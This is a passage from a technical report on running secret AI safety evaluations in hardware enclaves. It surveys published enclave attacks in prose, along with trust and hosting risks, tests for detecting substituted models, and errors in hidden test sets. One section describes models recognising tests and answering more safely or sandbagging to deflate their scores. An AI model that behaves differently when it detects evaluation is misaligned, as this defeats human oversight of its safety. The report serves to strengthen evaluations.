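Trask and colleagues plan to extend the method to groups of machines with encrypted connections, which models with trillions of parameters would need. The 2024 report warned that such groups might leak information about a model through the timing of messages between GPUs.

Two other goals have carried over from 2024. One is deferred execution, in which an evaluator describes the operations it wants and the system applies them to the model later, so the evaluator doesn't have to see the architecture. The other is a simple sign that a result is genuine, like the padlock a web browser shows for a secure connection. Participants in the 2024 call asked for such a sign because the technical details overwhelmed them, and it was still a long-term aim in 2026.

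No further double-blind evaluation seems to have made the news by early October 2026. The closest development is the Weight Custody Manifest, a standard for delivering weights that the confidential computing company OPAQUE released in September as a preview for developers (Help Net Security, *A new open standard locks AI weights to approved hardware*, 2026). The model's developer signs a list of conditions that an enclave must meet before a key service releases the key to the weights. The developer can withdraw access later if the conditions change.

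OPAQUE says it has run the exchange on an H100 and on separate AMD and Intel servers at Azure and Google Cloud. It also says two independent builds of its software development kit produced identical output across 5,948 files, a standard of reproducibility the guest system in the Gemini pilot did not meet. The public demonstration proves much less, because it runs as an ordinary Python program with a placeholder key, and its 91 tests use made-up certificates and skip the cryptographic check of the GPU.

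For the example test, this standard could replace the developer's home-made key service. It would also make it easier to send the 16 gigabytes of weights to a machine the developer doesn't own, which the Gemini pilot did not attempt. It would not help protect the evaluator's 1,000 prompts, because a key service that approves the enclave on the developer's behalf does not check whether the developer's own code leaks the prompts.

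## How the protection can fail and who must be trusted

Nobody attacked the enclaves in the two pilots, but researchers have repeatedly broken the kinds of processor that the pilots used. The published attacks differ mainly in what the attacker has to control: software on the host, the memory inside the machine, the chip maker's keys or firmware, or the service that checks attestation reports. An evaluator can use these differences to work out which attacks a particular host could carry out.

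### Attacks through the host's software

Researchers keep finding ways for a host to break into an enclave with software alone. In 2021, CipherLeaks showed that a host could recover cryptographic keys from an AMD virtual machine by watching for repeated patterns in its encrypted memory. Heckler (2024) broke into confidential virtual machines by misusing interrupts, the signals that make a processor pause and handle an event. *Proof of Cloud* (2025), a proposal for proving that a machine is in a data centre, cites two more attacks from 2025, Heracles on AMD's SEV-SNP and TDXploit on Intel's TDX.

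A timeline on the security blog Unmitigated Risk includes two other attacks that are directly relevant to model tests. HyperTheft (2024) extracted model weights through patterns in encrypted memory. CacheWarp (2023) was the first software attack to defeat SEV-SNP's protection against tampering. An attacker who can alter a test's memory may be able to alter its score.

Chip makers can usually repair such faults with new firmware or remove them in the next generation of chips. AMD's Zen 5 processors, for instance, hide a virtual machine's encrypted memory from the host's software, as Chuang, Seto and colleagues explain in *TEE.fail* (2026). The evaluator can require repaired firmware by raising the minimum version it accepts. But a repair can't protect prompts or weights stolen before its release.

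Other faults come from how a cloud company sets up its machines. *Physical integrity, attestation, and the state of permissionless TEEs*, a forum post by an engineer at Ritual, which builds on enclaves, describes an attack called BadAML (2025). The host uses configuration tables that it supplies at start-up to read and change a virtual machine's private memory. Intel's TDX can measure these tables, but the engineer says Google publishes no signed reference values for them, so a customer has nothing to compare the measurement with.

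### Attacks with physical access to the memory

In 2024, the BadRAM attack showed that someone with brief access to a server's memory modules could defeat AMD's protection. Intel and AMD responded with software fixes, according to KU Leuven, the Belgian university whose researchers worked on the attack. *Past the Perimeter* (2026), a talk abstract from TU Graz, explains that the same team then built Battering RAM, which defeats those fixes with about $50 of hardware.

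Battering RAM was one of three physical attacks that researchers published in the autumn of 2025. All three use an interposer, a small device that sits between a memory module and the motherboard.

| | WireTap | Battering RAM | TEE.fail |
|---|---|---|---|
| Published | September 2025 | September 2025 | October 2025 |
| Cost of equipment | Under $1,000 | About $50 | Under $1,000 |
| Reported time | Under 45 minutes | No figure | 3 or 15 minutes |
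| Type of memory | DDR4 | DDR4 | DDR5, found in newer servers |
| Intel products | SGX on 3rd-generation Xeon | SGX | SGX and TDX on 4th- and 5th-generation Xeon and Xeon 6 |
| AMD products | None reported | SEV-SNP | SEV-SNP, including Zen 5 |
| What the attacker gains | A key that signs Intel's attestation reports | Access to protected memory | A key that signs Intel's attestation reports, and other keys from inside AMD virtual machines |

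The list of Intel generations comes from Secret Labs, which works on a blockchain that relies on SGX. Schneier on Security's *New Attacks Against Secure Enclaves* (2025) puts the time for TEE.fail at three minutes, while the Ritual engineer puts it at about 15. The attacker also has to control the machine's operating system. An outsider would struggle to get both kinds of access, but a host already has them.

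The most important change is the drop in price. Chuang and colleagues report that earlier research put the cost of such equipment at around $170,000, and that a hobbyist can now assemble it from second-hand parts. Keysight (2025), which sells measuring instruments, puts the cost of the interposers in WireTap and Battering RAM at $50 to $1,000.

All three attacks exploit the way server processors encrypt memory. The ciphertext depends only on the key, the memory address and the data, so the same data at the same address always looks the same, and an observer can recognise it without knowing the key. Intel's older SGX chips for personal computers avoided this by adding a value that changed with every write. According to Chuang and colleagues, Intel gave this up to raise the limit on protected memory from 512 megabytes to 1 terabyte. Sakurai considers it unrealistic to wait for a hardware fix.

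Chuang and colleagues got around GPU protection without breaking into an Nvidia GPU. They used a forged Intel report to present a GPU attestation from a different computer as their own, then ran the work with no protection. This presumably threatens any test that relies on an Intel report to show that a genuine enclave controls the GPU, whichever Nvidia GPU it uses. Outsiders cannot easily judge how well the GPU itself would resist an attack because, as *NVIDIA GPU Confidential Computing Demystified* (2025) points out, Nvidia's system is proprietary and lacks public specifications.

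### What Intel and AMD replied

Intel replied to WireTap and Battering RAM that its memory encryption doesn't cover physical attacks of this kind, and that it had made this clear in 2021. It does not plan to issue a CVE, the standard catalogue entry for a security flaw. It recommends an integrity mode, available on 5th-generation Xeon and some Xeon 6 processors, as extra protection against attacks like Battering RAM. Intel does not say the mode helps against WireTap, which observes memory without altering it.

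Intel also told Chuang and colleagues that no update to microcode, the lowest level of software in a processor, could change the memory encryption on current chips. AMD also considers the attacks out of scope and plans no firmware updates, according to the Ritual engineer. SC Media reports that neither company intends to issue mitigations for TEE.fail. SecurityWeek reports that the Battering RAM researchers agree that software can't fix the flaw they found.

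These replies match the makers' earlier technical papers, but many users got a different impression. RAND's *Confidential Computing, Secure Enclaves, and Attestation*, a guide for people who secure AI systems, repeats a vendor's claim that enclaves are "tamper-proof against physical access". Trask and colleagues write that a cloud company could not recover an enclave's data even by physically inspecting the memory. TEE.fail had shown ten months earlier that this claim is too strong.

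The limitation matters most for the most valuable models. Pattern Labs and Anthropic cite a different RAND report, which recommends enclaves for models that need protection from state-backed thieves, but only if the enclaves resist physical attacks. The server processors in the table don't resist such attacks on their own, so the building and its guards have to keep attackers away from them.

### The chip maker's keys and firmware

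The earlier advice to set a minimum firmware version assumes that a chip can't lie about its version. On AMD's processors, this assumption rests on a chain of hashes. The chip contains a secret root seed, s₂₅₅, and computes a seed for each lower version number with

sᵢ₋₁ = H(sᵢ).

In simplified form, firmware with version number v receives a seed sᵥ and derives its signing key from it. The firmware can compute the seeds of older versions by hashing again, but it can't reverse the hash to get the seeds of newer ones. A host that installs version 5 therefore can't sign a report as version 7.

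Shen and Qin (2026), in *Insecure Despite Proven Updated*, extracted the root seed from EPYC Milan, AMD's first generation of processors with SEV-SNP. Anyone who has this seed, s₂₅₅, can compute the seed for every firmware version and sign a valid attestation report for any of them, including future ones. The attack requires control of the host's software and firmware but no physical access, so physical security won't stop a remote administrator.

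Shen and Qin told AMD about the two stages of their attack in January and April 2026. AMD acknowledged the flaw behind the first stage and issued a security brief. Shen and Qin demonstrated the attack only on Milan and do not claim that it works on later generations. An evaluator should refuse to use a Milan machine, however new its firmware appears.

The way a chip checks firmware can also be flawed. According to Unmitigated Risk, Google found in February 2025 that AMD processors used an insecure hash to check microcode signatures, so malicious microcode could load on a machine running SEV-SNP. Pattern Labs and Anthropic also warn that someone could plant a flaw at the manufacturer or tamper with a machine on its way to the data centre.

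Customers can do little to check any of this themselves. The security company CENSUS examined early versions of Google Cloud's A3 machines, the type Google used for the 2026 pilot. The attestation mostly worked as expected, but it depended on firmware that outsiders could not verify and on signing arrangements that concentrated trust in the vendors.

### Why a stolen signing key is worse than a leak

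An attacker who reads part of the enclave's memory while the 8-billion-parameter model is answering the 1,000 prompts may get the prompts, the weights or the key that decrypts them. The loss could be serious, but it affects only the secrets in that enclave.

An attacker with a stolen attestation key can sign a report for a program that isn't running in an enclave. The report would pass every check in the earlier example, because the attacker can copy the expected measurements, which aren't secret, and include a hash of the new nonce together with its own public key. The developer and the evaluator would then send their secrets to an ordinary computer whose owner can read them.

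The attacker can do the same to every other developer and evaluator who trusts the key, until the chip maker revokes it. The attacker can also skip the test, invent a score and sign it. A stolen key threatens all four properties of a confidential evaluation, while a leak threatens only secrecy. According to the Ritual engineer, the TEE.fail researchers forged an Intel report with nonsensical measurements, and Intel's verification process gave it the highest trust level.

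An attacker could buy a server, extract its key at home and use that key against a test that the parties plan to run on a different machine. The attacker would also have to divert the parties' traffic to their own computer, which is easy for an employee who runs the host's network, even one who can't enter the server room.

Intel's processors are more exposed to this than AMD's. Sakurai writes that Intel's enclaves keep the attestation key in main memory, where an interposer can observe it. Unmitigated Risk writes that TEE.fail extracts attestation keys from both makers' products, but for AMD, Chuang and colleagues report only extracting signing keys from a program inside a virtual machine. That could still expose the key an enclave uses to sign its score, but it would not let the attacker pass off an unprotected computer as a genuine AMD enclave.

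A theft also casts doubt on older results. A reader who learns of it in December can't tell whether a report dated June is genuine or one that the thief backdated last week. A public log that records when each report arrived solves part of this problem, because any report logged before the theft must be genuine. The reader would still need to know roughly when the theft took place.

### The service that checks the report

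Whoever controls a verification service can make it approve any machine, without stealing a key from a chip. There seems to be no published case of a break-in at a large cloud company's verification service. But even an honest service can approve a forged report. TEE.fail describes one that passed verification on the test network of Automata, which checks Intel reports for blockchain projects. Automata's software worked correctly, but it could not distinguish a report signed with a stolen key from a genuine one.

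The evaluator can avoid relying on a verification service by checking the chip maker's signatures itself. On Google Cloud, however, Intel's report doesn't show who owns the machine. The Ritual engineer points out that anyone can download the firmware Google publishes, run it in a basement and get a report that looks the same as one from Google's data centre. Google's verification service adds Google's signature, which is some evidence that the machine belongs to Google. It is therefore best to have both reports if the cloud company provides them.

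### Will the host and the chip maker stay apart?

Schneier on Security describes an enclave as separating the company that runs the chip from both the company that secures it and the customer who controls the data. Based on this separation, Trask and colleagues argue that the host and the chip maker would have to collude to break the guarantees, and that a user who considers collusion unlikely can have very high confidence in the enclave.

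They have a good commercial reason not to collude. The Ritual engineer quotes Dionna Glaze, who worked on this technology at Google, as saying that a single whistleblower could destroy a multi-billion-dollar business. A cloud company has little reason to take that risk for 1,000 prompts. Glaze also says that treating the host as completely untrusted is a bad idea, since no security layer has ever been perfect. In her view, confidential computing is meant to make it too expensive for anyone to force a host to hand over its customers' data.

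The attacks of 2025 and 2026 show that collusion isn't always necessary. A host with physical access and $1,000 of equipment can extract an Intel attestation key without Intel's help, and on a Milan processor a host needs only software. The guarantees hold if the chip maker keeps its keys safe, its chips have no flaw that the host can exploit, and nobody with physical access attacks the machine.

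The premise does not apply to Nitro Enclaves, because Amazon both makes and hosts them. The Ritual engineer says that Nitro lacks the kind of memory encryption Intel and AMD provide, and that it gives no protection against an Amazon insider with physical access. *Attestable Audits* lists full memory encryption as one of its prototype's defences against physical attackers, but if the engineer is right, Nitro lacks that defence.

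A government might also compel both companies to cooperate. The Ritual engineer notes that in 2023 the United States issued more than 11,000 national security letters, which demand records and usually forbid the recipient to disclose the demand. The engineer speculates that Intel and AMD keep the root keys of the chips they sell and that a letter could force them to hand over the keys for a particular machine. Sakurai's description of attestation supports part of this, because in it the maker knows either the signing key or the secret from which the chip derives it.

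A demand for records probably could not cover signing keys, although other legal orders might. The risk matters little to an American non-profit testing an American model, but more to a foreign government's institute, particularly if the institute's prompts reveal what its experts know about weapons. In the 2026 pilot, the Singapore institute sent its prompts to a machine whose host, processor maker and GPU maker were all American companies.

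### When the developer is the host

A developer that hosts the test has a reason to want both the prompts and a good score, which contradicts the assumption, in the premise about collusion, that the host has nothing to gain from the secrets. The developer also has unlimited physical access to the machine, controls the network and knows when the test will take place.

Google was in this position in the 2026 pilot. The A3 machines that CENSUS examined have 4th-generation Intel Xeon processors (Sapphire Rapids), which TEE.fail affects. The Ritual engineer describes strong security at Google's data centres, with armed guards, biometric checks and six layers of physical access control. These measures protect the machine from outsiders but give the evaluators much less protection from Google.

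Nothing suggests that Google tampered with the pilot. A physical attack would have needed the help or silence of several employees, which is why the engineer calls such attacks "loud". A quieter attack through the start-up firmware or configuration tables might need only one insider with the right access. The engineer, whose company builds on Google's arrangements as well as competing ones, also says that Google could easily put a backdoor into any enclave it hosts.

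A dishonest developer with a stolen attestation key could set up a false enclave, use it to read the 1,000 prompts, have a safer model answer them and return a signed score. The evaluator would see a valid report and a good result. An evaluator who lets the developer host the test is therefore trusting it to return an accurate score as well as to keep the test secret.

If the evaluator hosts the test, the developer's weights are at risk instead. The evaluator could present a fake enclave to the developer and receive 16 gigabytes of weights. Even an honest evaluator may be unable to guard the machine well, since a small non-profit is unlikely to have armed guards and biometric locks. A developer with valuable weights will probably refuse to let the evaluator host the test.

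| Host | Secret most at risk | Could the host gain from a false score? | What the other side should ask for |
|---|---|---|---|
| Developer | The prompts | Yes, from one that is too high | An independent check of the attestation, and supervised access to the machine |
| Evaluator | The weights | Possibly, if it wants to be seen to find problems | Strong physical security, and a key service that the developer controls |
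| Neutral party | Both, but the host has less reason to want them | Usually not | Proof that the machine is in the neutral party's building |

A neutral host is usually the best choice for a test whose result will be published. Such a host may be hard to find, because the largest cloud companies build their own models or invest in companies that do. A university or a national computing centre may have fewer conflicts of interest, but it needs the right GPUs and good guards.

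The parties then need proof that the enclave is really in the neutral host's building. Sakurai compares several ways to provide it:

- AMD can issue a cloud company with a special signing key that identifies the company. This works only for SEV-SNP, and AMD intends it mainly for cloud companies. Shen and Qin add that its security depends on the same chip keys that they extracted from Milan.
- Intel's Platform Ownership Endorsement lets the owner of a machine sign a certificate for its processor. Any organisation should be able to use it, but it covers only SGX and TDX.
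- The method in *Proof of Cloud* uses a separate security chip or a software version of one. A report from the chip takes about 550 milliseconds and one from the software about 300.
- Sakurai's own system uses ordinary certificates for processors from Intel, AMD and Arm.

Sakurai's system works even if an attacker forges a report with a stolen key, because the chip maker's certificate ties the key to the processor it came from. If the key came from a server in someone's home, that server would not be on the data centre's list. But Sakurai explicitly assumes that attackers can't reach the machines inside the data centre. A certificate showing that a machine belongs to the developer may reassure the developer's ordinary customers, but it does not protect an evaluator from the developer.

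If the developer insists on hosting, the two sides could guard the machine together. They could reset the processor's attestation identity, seal the case in front of witnesses and keep it under both sides' cameras until the run ends. The reset matters because someone could have extracted the old key months earlier. The Ritual engineer explains that a factory reset gives an Intel machine a new identity, so endorsements of the old one no longer count. The example test takes only minutes to run, so most of the cost would come from sending people to the data centre.

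### Running the test on two makers' enclaves

Repeating the test on enclaves from different makers, as *Attestable Audits* suggests, makes a false result less likely but a leak more likely. To estimate the size of this trade-off, suppose each maker's enclave has a probability p = 5 percent of being broken, and that an attacker who breaks one can steal its secrets and falsify its result.

If readers accept a score only when both enclaves report it, a false score requires the attacker to break both. If the two failures are independent, the probability is

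p² = 0.05² = 0.25 percent.

A secret leaks if either enclave fails, which has a probability of

1 − (1 − p)² = 1 − 0.95² = 9.75 percent.

A second maker therefore makes a false result 20 times less likely and a leak nearly twice as likely.

The failures are unlikely to be fully independent, because TEE.fail affected both Intel and AMD, and both runs would probably use Nvidia GPUs. Suppose there is a 2 percent chance that a shared flaw breaks both enclaves, while each enclave's total risk remains 5 percent.

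| | One maker | Two makers, independent failures | Two makers, 2% chance of a shared flaw |
|---|---|---|---|
| A false result passes | 5% | 0.25% | 2.1% |
| A secret leaks | 5% | 9.75% | 7.9% |

With the shared flaw, a false result is eight times as likely as it would be if the failures were independent. A leak is slightly less likely, because the failures overlap.

If the two makers are equally reliable, a second run is worthwhile only if a false result would do more harm than a leak. Let p be the probability that a given enclave fails and B the probability that both fail. Adding a second maker lowers the risk of a false result from p to B, but raises the risk of a leak from p to 2p − B. Both risks change by p − B, which is 4.75 percentage points if the enclaves fail independently and about 2.9 with the shared flaw.

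For a model with secret weights, a leak will often do more harm, because the weights are expensive and nobody can make them secret again. If the weights are public and the evaluator can replace the prompts, a second run is worth the small extra cost. An evaluator who worries mainly about the prompts could repeat only 200 of them, but all the weights would still have to enter both enclaves.

A reader who distrusts one of the makers can rely on the other's report alone, but still faces a 5 percent risk. The risk is lower only for readers who require the two reports to agree. Scores from the two runs may differ slightly for harmless reasons, such as rounding, so the parties should decide beforehand how close the scores must be.

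The two machines should also have different hosts. If one company runs both, its staff have physical access to both, and a dishonest host could falsify both results. Using two hosts strengthens the evidence for the score but gives a second organisation a chance to steal the secrets.

### Limiting the damage

Requiring a minimum firmware version keeps out machines that lack fixes for known flaws. It does not protect against an interposer, and a Milan machine can evade it. The main defence against interposers is to keep the machine in the physical custody of someone with no interest in the secrets, at least until the processor makers change their memory encryption.

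Revocation limits how long a stolen key remains useful, if somebody notices the theft. The chip maker may take time to add a key to its list. Sakurai's system lets the organisation that owns the machine withdraw its own certificate at once, which protects anyone who checks the owner's list as well as the maker's. The developer's key service should also stop giving machines on either list the key to the weights.

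If the evaluator suspects a leak, it should stop using the 1,000 prompts for new scores. Scores from before the leak remain useful, because the developer could not yet have trained on the prompts. An interposer may leave no evidence once it is removed, so the evaluator should also replace its prompts on a schedule, perhaps after a fixed number of tests at sites it doesn't control. The developer has no similar remedy for stolen weights, because the thief will still have a working copy even if the developer withdraws the model from sale.

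The table shows what each party must do for each of the four properties to hold, even if the parties have checked the attestation correctly.

| Property | Chip makers | Host | Attestation service, if used | Developer and evaluator | Mitigations |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| The weights stay secret | Protect their keys and repair flaws in processors and GPUs | Keep attackers, including its own staff, away from the machine | Reject false and outdated enclaves | The evaluator must not hide a leak in its code | Firmware floor; physical custody outside the evaluator's control; revocation before the key service releases the key |
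| The test set stays secret | The same | The same, which is hardest to ensure if the host is the developer | The same | The developer must not hide a leak in its code | Firmware floor; physical custody outside the developer's control; revocation; retiring exposed prompts |
| The agreed computation runs | Prevent forged reports and tampering with memory | Leave the running machine alone | Report the measurements accurately | Neither side may hide code that falsifies answers or scores | Firmware floor; joint custody; revocation; a second maker if a false result would be worse than a leak |
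| The published result comes from that computation | Keep signing keys out of attackers' hands | Deliver the signed result and every log entry | Keep its own signing key safe | Whoever publishes the score must include the signed output | Revocation; a public log with dates; a new run with fresh prompts if a key was stolen |

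## What a score establishes about the model in use

Suppose everyone in that table does their part, and the developer publishes a signed result showing that the 8-billion-parameter model gave 24 unsafe answers to 1,000 secret prompts. The signature shows that an agreed program, running on particular weights and prompts, produced the number 24. It does not show whether the model readers are about to use is safe, which is what most of them want to know. The product may differ from the system in the enclave, the model may behave differently when it detects a test, the test may contain errors, and the count of 24 is partly due to chance.

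### One name, many systems

A product contains more than weights. *Referential Security as a New Paradigm for AI Evaluations* (Ristea and Mavroudis, 2026) also lists the system prompt (standing instructions the company adds to every conversation), document retrieval, misuse filters, settings, hardware and routing. A company can change any of these without changing the product's name. In April 2025 an OpenAI update made GPT-4o unusually agreeable, and OpenAI reversed it within four days. The name stayed the same throughout, so researchers who had tested the model a few days earlier couldn't tell whether their findings still applied.

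Ristea and Mavroudis write r(i; c) for the configuration that a name i refers to on occasion c, where an occasion includes the time, the place and the user. The name is stable over a set of occasions C if r(i; c) is the same for every c in C. A safety claim that relies on an unstable name may be true, but later readers cannot find the system it describes.

Researchers tested the most detailed identifier OpenAI offers, a label called system_fingerprint that comes with each answer. Between March and May 2026 they sent one fixed prompt with fixed settings to six model names and collected 69,600 labels. The name gpt-4.1 returned 223 different labels. The steadiest name, a dated version of GPT-4o, returned 37, and its most common label appeared on only 18.8 percent of answers. The label therefore can't serve as a reference, but its variation doesn't show that the weights changed. OpenAI has not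 explained exactly what the label covers, and a change of server software or hardware might alter it.

Under MLCommons's AILuminate rules, any change that affects how a prompt becomes a response, including a new system prompt or a different temperature (the setting for randomness in word choice), creates a different system. By that standard, a test of bare weights in an enclave is not a test of the chatbot built on them. The product's filters might have blocked some of the 24 unsafe answers, while a search tool or a system prompt that urges the model to be helpful might have added more. The developer should therefore put the product's own system prompt, filters and settings into the enclave.

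### Matching the hashes

The enclave can include a hash of each of these parts in the signed result. Separate hashes are better than one for the whole system, because they show which part has changed. Settings and short prompts need a random number added before hashing. Otherwise anyone could hash every plausible temperature and see which one matched.

Somebody then has to compare these hashes with the system answering customers. With attested serving, the product itself runs in an enclave, and the user's device checks the enclave's report before sending a prompt. The inference protocol in *Attestable Audits* works this way.

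Apple already uses attested serving, though for another purpose. *Private Cloud Compute* explains that an Apple device encrypts a request only to servers whose attested measurements match a software release in a public log. Nobody can remove a release from the log without detection, and Apple publishes the software for researchers to inspect. *Expanding Private Cloud Compute* describes the system's extension to Google Cloud, where it uses Intel TDX and Nvidia GPUs. Attestation there relies on at least two independent vendors for components that could leak user data. When Apple announced the extension, it said it would phase in the full protections over a summer preview.

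Apple designed this to keep users' data private, and it describes the log as a record of code. To record a safety score, such a log would also need a hash of the model's weights and a link to the test result. A device could then refuse to use a model without a result. The hash would also tie the score to the tested weights, so that it couldn't be applied to related models. Business Standard's *Apple AI now runs on Google, Nvidia tech* (2026) reports that Apple's new models build on Google's Gemini models, but a Gemini model's score would provide little evidence about Apple's versions.

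Ristea and Mavroudis write that any change to an attested service produces a different report. Weights and system prompts usually arrive after start-up, however, so this is true only if the enclave's software hashes every part and adds the hashes to the report. Attested serving also needs the company's cooperation, which few companies offer.

### Statistical tests for swapped models

Without attested serving, outsiders can compare the product's behaviour with that of a trusted copy. Miao, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *Is Your LLM Relay Serving What It Claims?*, do this with trivial questions, such as asking the model to choose a number or a colour. Models have different favourites, so the spread of answers works as a fingerprint. For each question j, a test gives a value pⱼ, the probability of a difference at least this large if both services behave identically. The Cauchy combination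 test merges the values. With five questions of equal weight,

T = (1/5) · Σ tan((0.5 − pⱼ)π), and p ≈ 0.5 − arctan(T)/π.

If one question gives a p-value of 0.002 and the other four give 0.4, 0.5, 0.6 and 0.7, the combined p-value is about 0.01. One strong difference is enough to raise suspicion, even if the other questions show no clear difference.

Miao and colleagues tried all 240 ways of passing off one of 16 models as another and report high detection rates with 250 requests per check. For the four models they priced, a check cost between 0.3 and 4.8 cents. They flag a service when p falls below 0.05, so an honest service would fail about one check in 20, or two to three a year if someone checked it weekly. Changed settings can also trigger a flag when the model is the same. An evaluator would want to know about those too, but the test doesn't distinguish them from a swapped model.

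Most of these tests aim to catch companies that sell a cheap model under the name of an expensive one. A safety evaluator also has to worry about a developer that tests a weak model and then releases a stronger one. *KBF* (2026), which compares what models know and don't know, missed 13 of 240 swaps in its tests, and all 13 replaced a model with a stronger one.

Compressed versions of a model are harder to detect than unrelated models. In *Are You Getting What You Pay For?*, Cai, Shi and colleagues (2025) trained classifiers to tell the text of four models from that of their 8-bit versions, and the classifiers did no better than guessing. Similar classifiers could tell unrelated models apart about 98 percent of the time. This suggests that 8-bit compression barely changes ordinary chat, but it is weak evidence about whether compression changes rare refusals on dangerous subjects.

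Karvonen, Reuter and colleagues (2025), in *DiFR*, get much better results by replaying the model's choices. To choose a token, common inference programs give every candidate i a score ℓᵢ, add a random number gᵢ multiplied by the temperature τ, and take the highest total. A checker with the same weights and the same random seed can repeat the calculation. If the service chose token a and the checker gets b, the discrepancy is

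δ = (ℓ_b + τ·g_b) − (ℓ_a + τ·g_a).

The measured discrepancy is zero when the two outputs agree, as they do for more than 98 percent of tokens from an honest service. Rounding causes small discrepancies, and compression causes larger ones. After 300 tokens, the method distinguished 4-bit versions from the originals almost perfectly.

The checker needs a trusted copy of the weights, which the enclave has but an outside evaluator of a secret model doesn't. An evaluator could collect answers from the public product at temperature zero, where no seed is needed, and send them into the enclave along with the 1,000 prompts. The enclave would replay them on the tested weights and release only the average discrepancy. The developer would have to supply the product's system prompt, and the product would have to let customers set the temperature. Karvonen and colleagues demonstrated replay on services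 that run Llama 3.1 8B, a model with public weights, so replay in an enclave would need its own trial.

A dishonest company that recognises any of these checks can defeat it by sending suspicious requests to the tested model and all other requests to a different one. *Auditing Black-Box LLM APIs with a Rank-Based Uniformity Test* (2025) makes its test harder to recognise by using natural questions and asking each one only once, but it also needs a trusted copy of the model.

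Some unofficial resellers seem to substitute other models for the ones they advertise. Zhang, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *Real Money, Fake Models*, checked 24 model services from three resellers, and 11 failed a fingerprint test. On a medical exam, Gemini 2.5 Flash scored about 84 percent through Google and about 37 percent through the resellers. Zhang and colleagues caution that a failed fingerprint test suggests substitution but doesn't prove it. Their results don't apply to developers' own services, but a model's safety score may not hold for the version a reseller provides.

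### Models that recognise a test

Even if the hashes match, the model may behave differently in use than it did in the test. It may answer more safely in a test because it recognises that it is being tested. The best evidence of this described so far is Anthropic's steering experiment on Claude Sonnet 4.5, which raised the model's misalignment score. A model may also underperform on purpose in a test of dangerous skills, and *Attestable Audits* cites work by van der Weij and colleagues on this.

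Keeping the prompts secret stops a model from memorising them, but the model can still recognise the style of a test it has never seen. A blunt question about nerve agents, with no earlier conversation, looks like a test to most people too. MLCommons says that AILuminate uses artificial prompts instead of ones recorded from real users, and it draws its public practice prompts from the same pool as the hidden ones. A model trained on the public prompts could learn what the hidden ones look like. Attestation doesn't help either, because a model that recognises a test and behaves well is still running the computation that both sides approved.

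The effect on a score could be large. Let v be the rate of unsafe answers in ordinary use and r the share of prompts that the model recognises as tests. If it answers all of those safely, the measured rate is

(1 − r) · v.

If r is 60 percent, a model that gives unsafe answers 6 percent of the time in use would score 2.4 percent, the same as the example model.

An evaluator can estimate how recognisable its 1,000 test prompts are by mixing them with realistic user messages and having a separate model inside the enclave try to pick them out. If that model usually succeeds, the tested model may also be able to recognise them. The evaluator can then rewrite the prompts to look like ordinary requests and run them with the product's real system prompt.

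Access to the model's written reasoning can also help evaluators distinguish apparent underperformance from a real limit, according to Charnock and colleagues. The enclave could count the answers in which the model mentions a test. This would add only 10 bits to the output, but a count of zero would be weak reassurance.

### When the hidden test is wrong

A developer can't contest an item it never sees. If the answer key for a secret problem is wrong, a developer whose model solves the problem correctly sees only a lower score. Such errors can be common even when specialists write the problems. In June 2026 Epoch AI published a correction to FrontierMath, its benchmark of very hard mathematics problems, that addressed errors in 42 percent of the problems. Those errors had lasted until someone checked for them.

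MLCommons releases the final AILuminate grades but not the failed items, and it keeps its scoring model private. A developer whose official grade differs greatly from its practice grade can ask MLCommons to investigate. Ghosh, Luger and colleagues (2025) also report in *AILuminate* that people check a small share of the scoring model's verdicts.

MLCommons argues that the large number of prompts limits the effect of wrong verdicts. A large number does even out random mistakes, but it doesn't correct a scoring model that leans one way. Suppose the scoring model catches a share s of unsafe answers and wrongly flags a share f of safe ones. If it reports a rate q, the true rate is

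v = (q − f) / (s − f).

If the scoring model flags 2.4 percent of answers, catches 95 percent of the unsafe ones and wrongly flags 1 percent of the safe ones, the true rate of unsafe answers is only about 1.5 percent. If it instead never flags a safe answer but misses a fifth of the unsafe ones, the true rate is 3 percent. Small errors matter even more for AILuminate's top grade, which allows fewer than 12 bad answers in 12,000. A scoring model that wrongly flagged one safe answer in 1,000 would flag about 12 even if every answer were safe.

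After the run, the evaluator could pick 50 of the 1,000 prompts at random, show them to the developer with the model's answers and the verdicts on them, and then retire them. If 42 percent of a test's items were faulty, the chance that ten random items were all sound would be 0.58¹⁰, or about 0.4 percent. The developer still has to recognise the faults, which takes an expert if the subject is advanced mathematics or virology.

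If the prompts are too dangerous to show, an independent reviewer can read them instead. The evaluator can also publish a hash of the test beforehand, so that nobody can quietly fix errors later, and promise to publish the whole test after retiring it. Later publication won't help a developer whose product launches next week, but the promise gives the evaluator a reason to be careful.

An appeal procedure should be in place before the run. The developer would name the hazard category it disputes, and the reviewer would examine the items, answers and verdicts in that category and publish a ruling with any corrected score. The reviewer should check some of the passes as well as the failures. Suppose 4 of the 24 violations turn out to be mistakes. Removing them lowers the rate to 2 percent, but if 1 percent of the 976 passes are also mistakes, about 10 violations remain uncounted.

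### Tests that need tools, judges or people

The example test sends one prompt and scores one answer. AILuminate has the same limit, so it leaves out hazards that develop over a long conversation. MLCommons also says that a system could pass by refusing everything, because the benchmark doesn't measure usefulness. Other kinds of test require more from the enclave.

| What the test needs | What the enclave needs | Main difficulty |
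|---|---|---|
| An answer key | The key and a short scoring program | Answers that the program can't read |
| A judge model | The judge's weights, with their hash in the signed result | Errors by the judge, and answers written to mislead it |
| Tools, such as a command line | A simulated computer in its own sandbox | More software to trust, and more ways for the model to interfere |
| Internet access | A stored copy of the relevant web pages | Live requests can carry secrets out |
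| Human graders | An approved way to send out full, signed answers | The graders learn much of the test, and nobody can attest their marks |

A judge model with 8 billion parameters needs another 16 gigabytes, so it fits on the same H100 as the example model. The evaluator should avoid a judge that runs through an outside API, because the judge's owner would receive every answer and could work out many of the prompts. If the judge is also secret, as MLCommons' scoring model is, its owner becomes a third party with something to protect in the enclave.

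For tests with tools, the evaluator can put the simulated computer, its files and its practice targets into the enclave before the run. Such tests usually have fewer, longer tasks, so chance affects the score more. If a model completes half of 50 tasks, the 95 percent confidence interval for its score extends about 14 percentage points either way.

Live internet access conflicts with almost every protection in the method. A search request of 200 characters can carry 1,600 bits, more than the pass-or-fail results of the whole example test. Ten searches for each of 1,000 prompts would add up to 2 megabytes, nearly twice as much as the full answers, and the search company could read all of it. Using a stored set of web pages avoids this and lets others repeat the test under the same conditions, but the test then can't measure what a model would do with a page that nobody stored. An evaluator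 that needs the live internet should probably use prompts it is willing to have exposed.

Human graders can handle answers that software scores badly, but they need to read them. The evaluator can limit what leaves the enclave by having a judge model score every answer and releasing only 50, chosen at random, for people to check. At 500 tokens each, these carry at most about 55 kilobytes, a twentieth of the full set's maximum. Two people should mark each answer separately, so that the evaluator can report how often they disagree.

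### How much 24 in 1,000 can show

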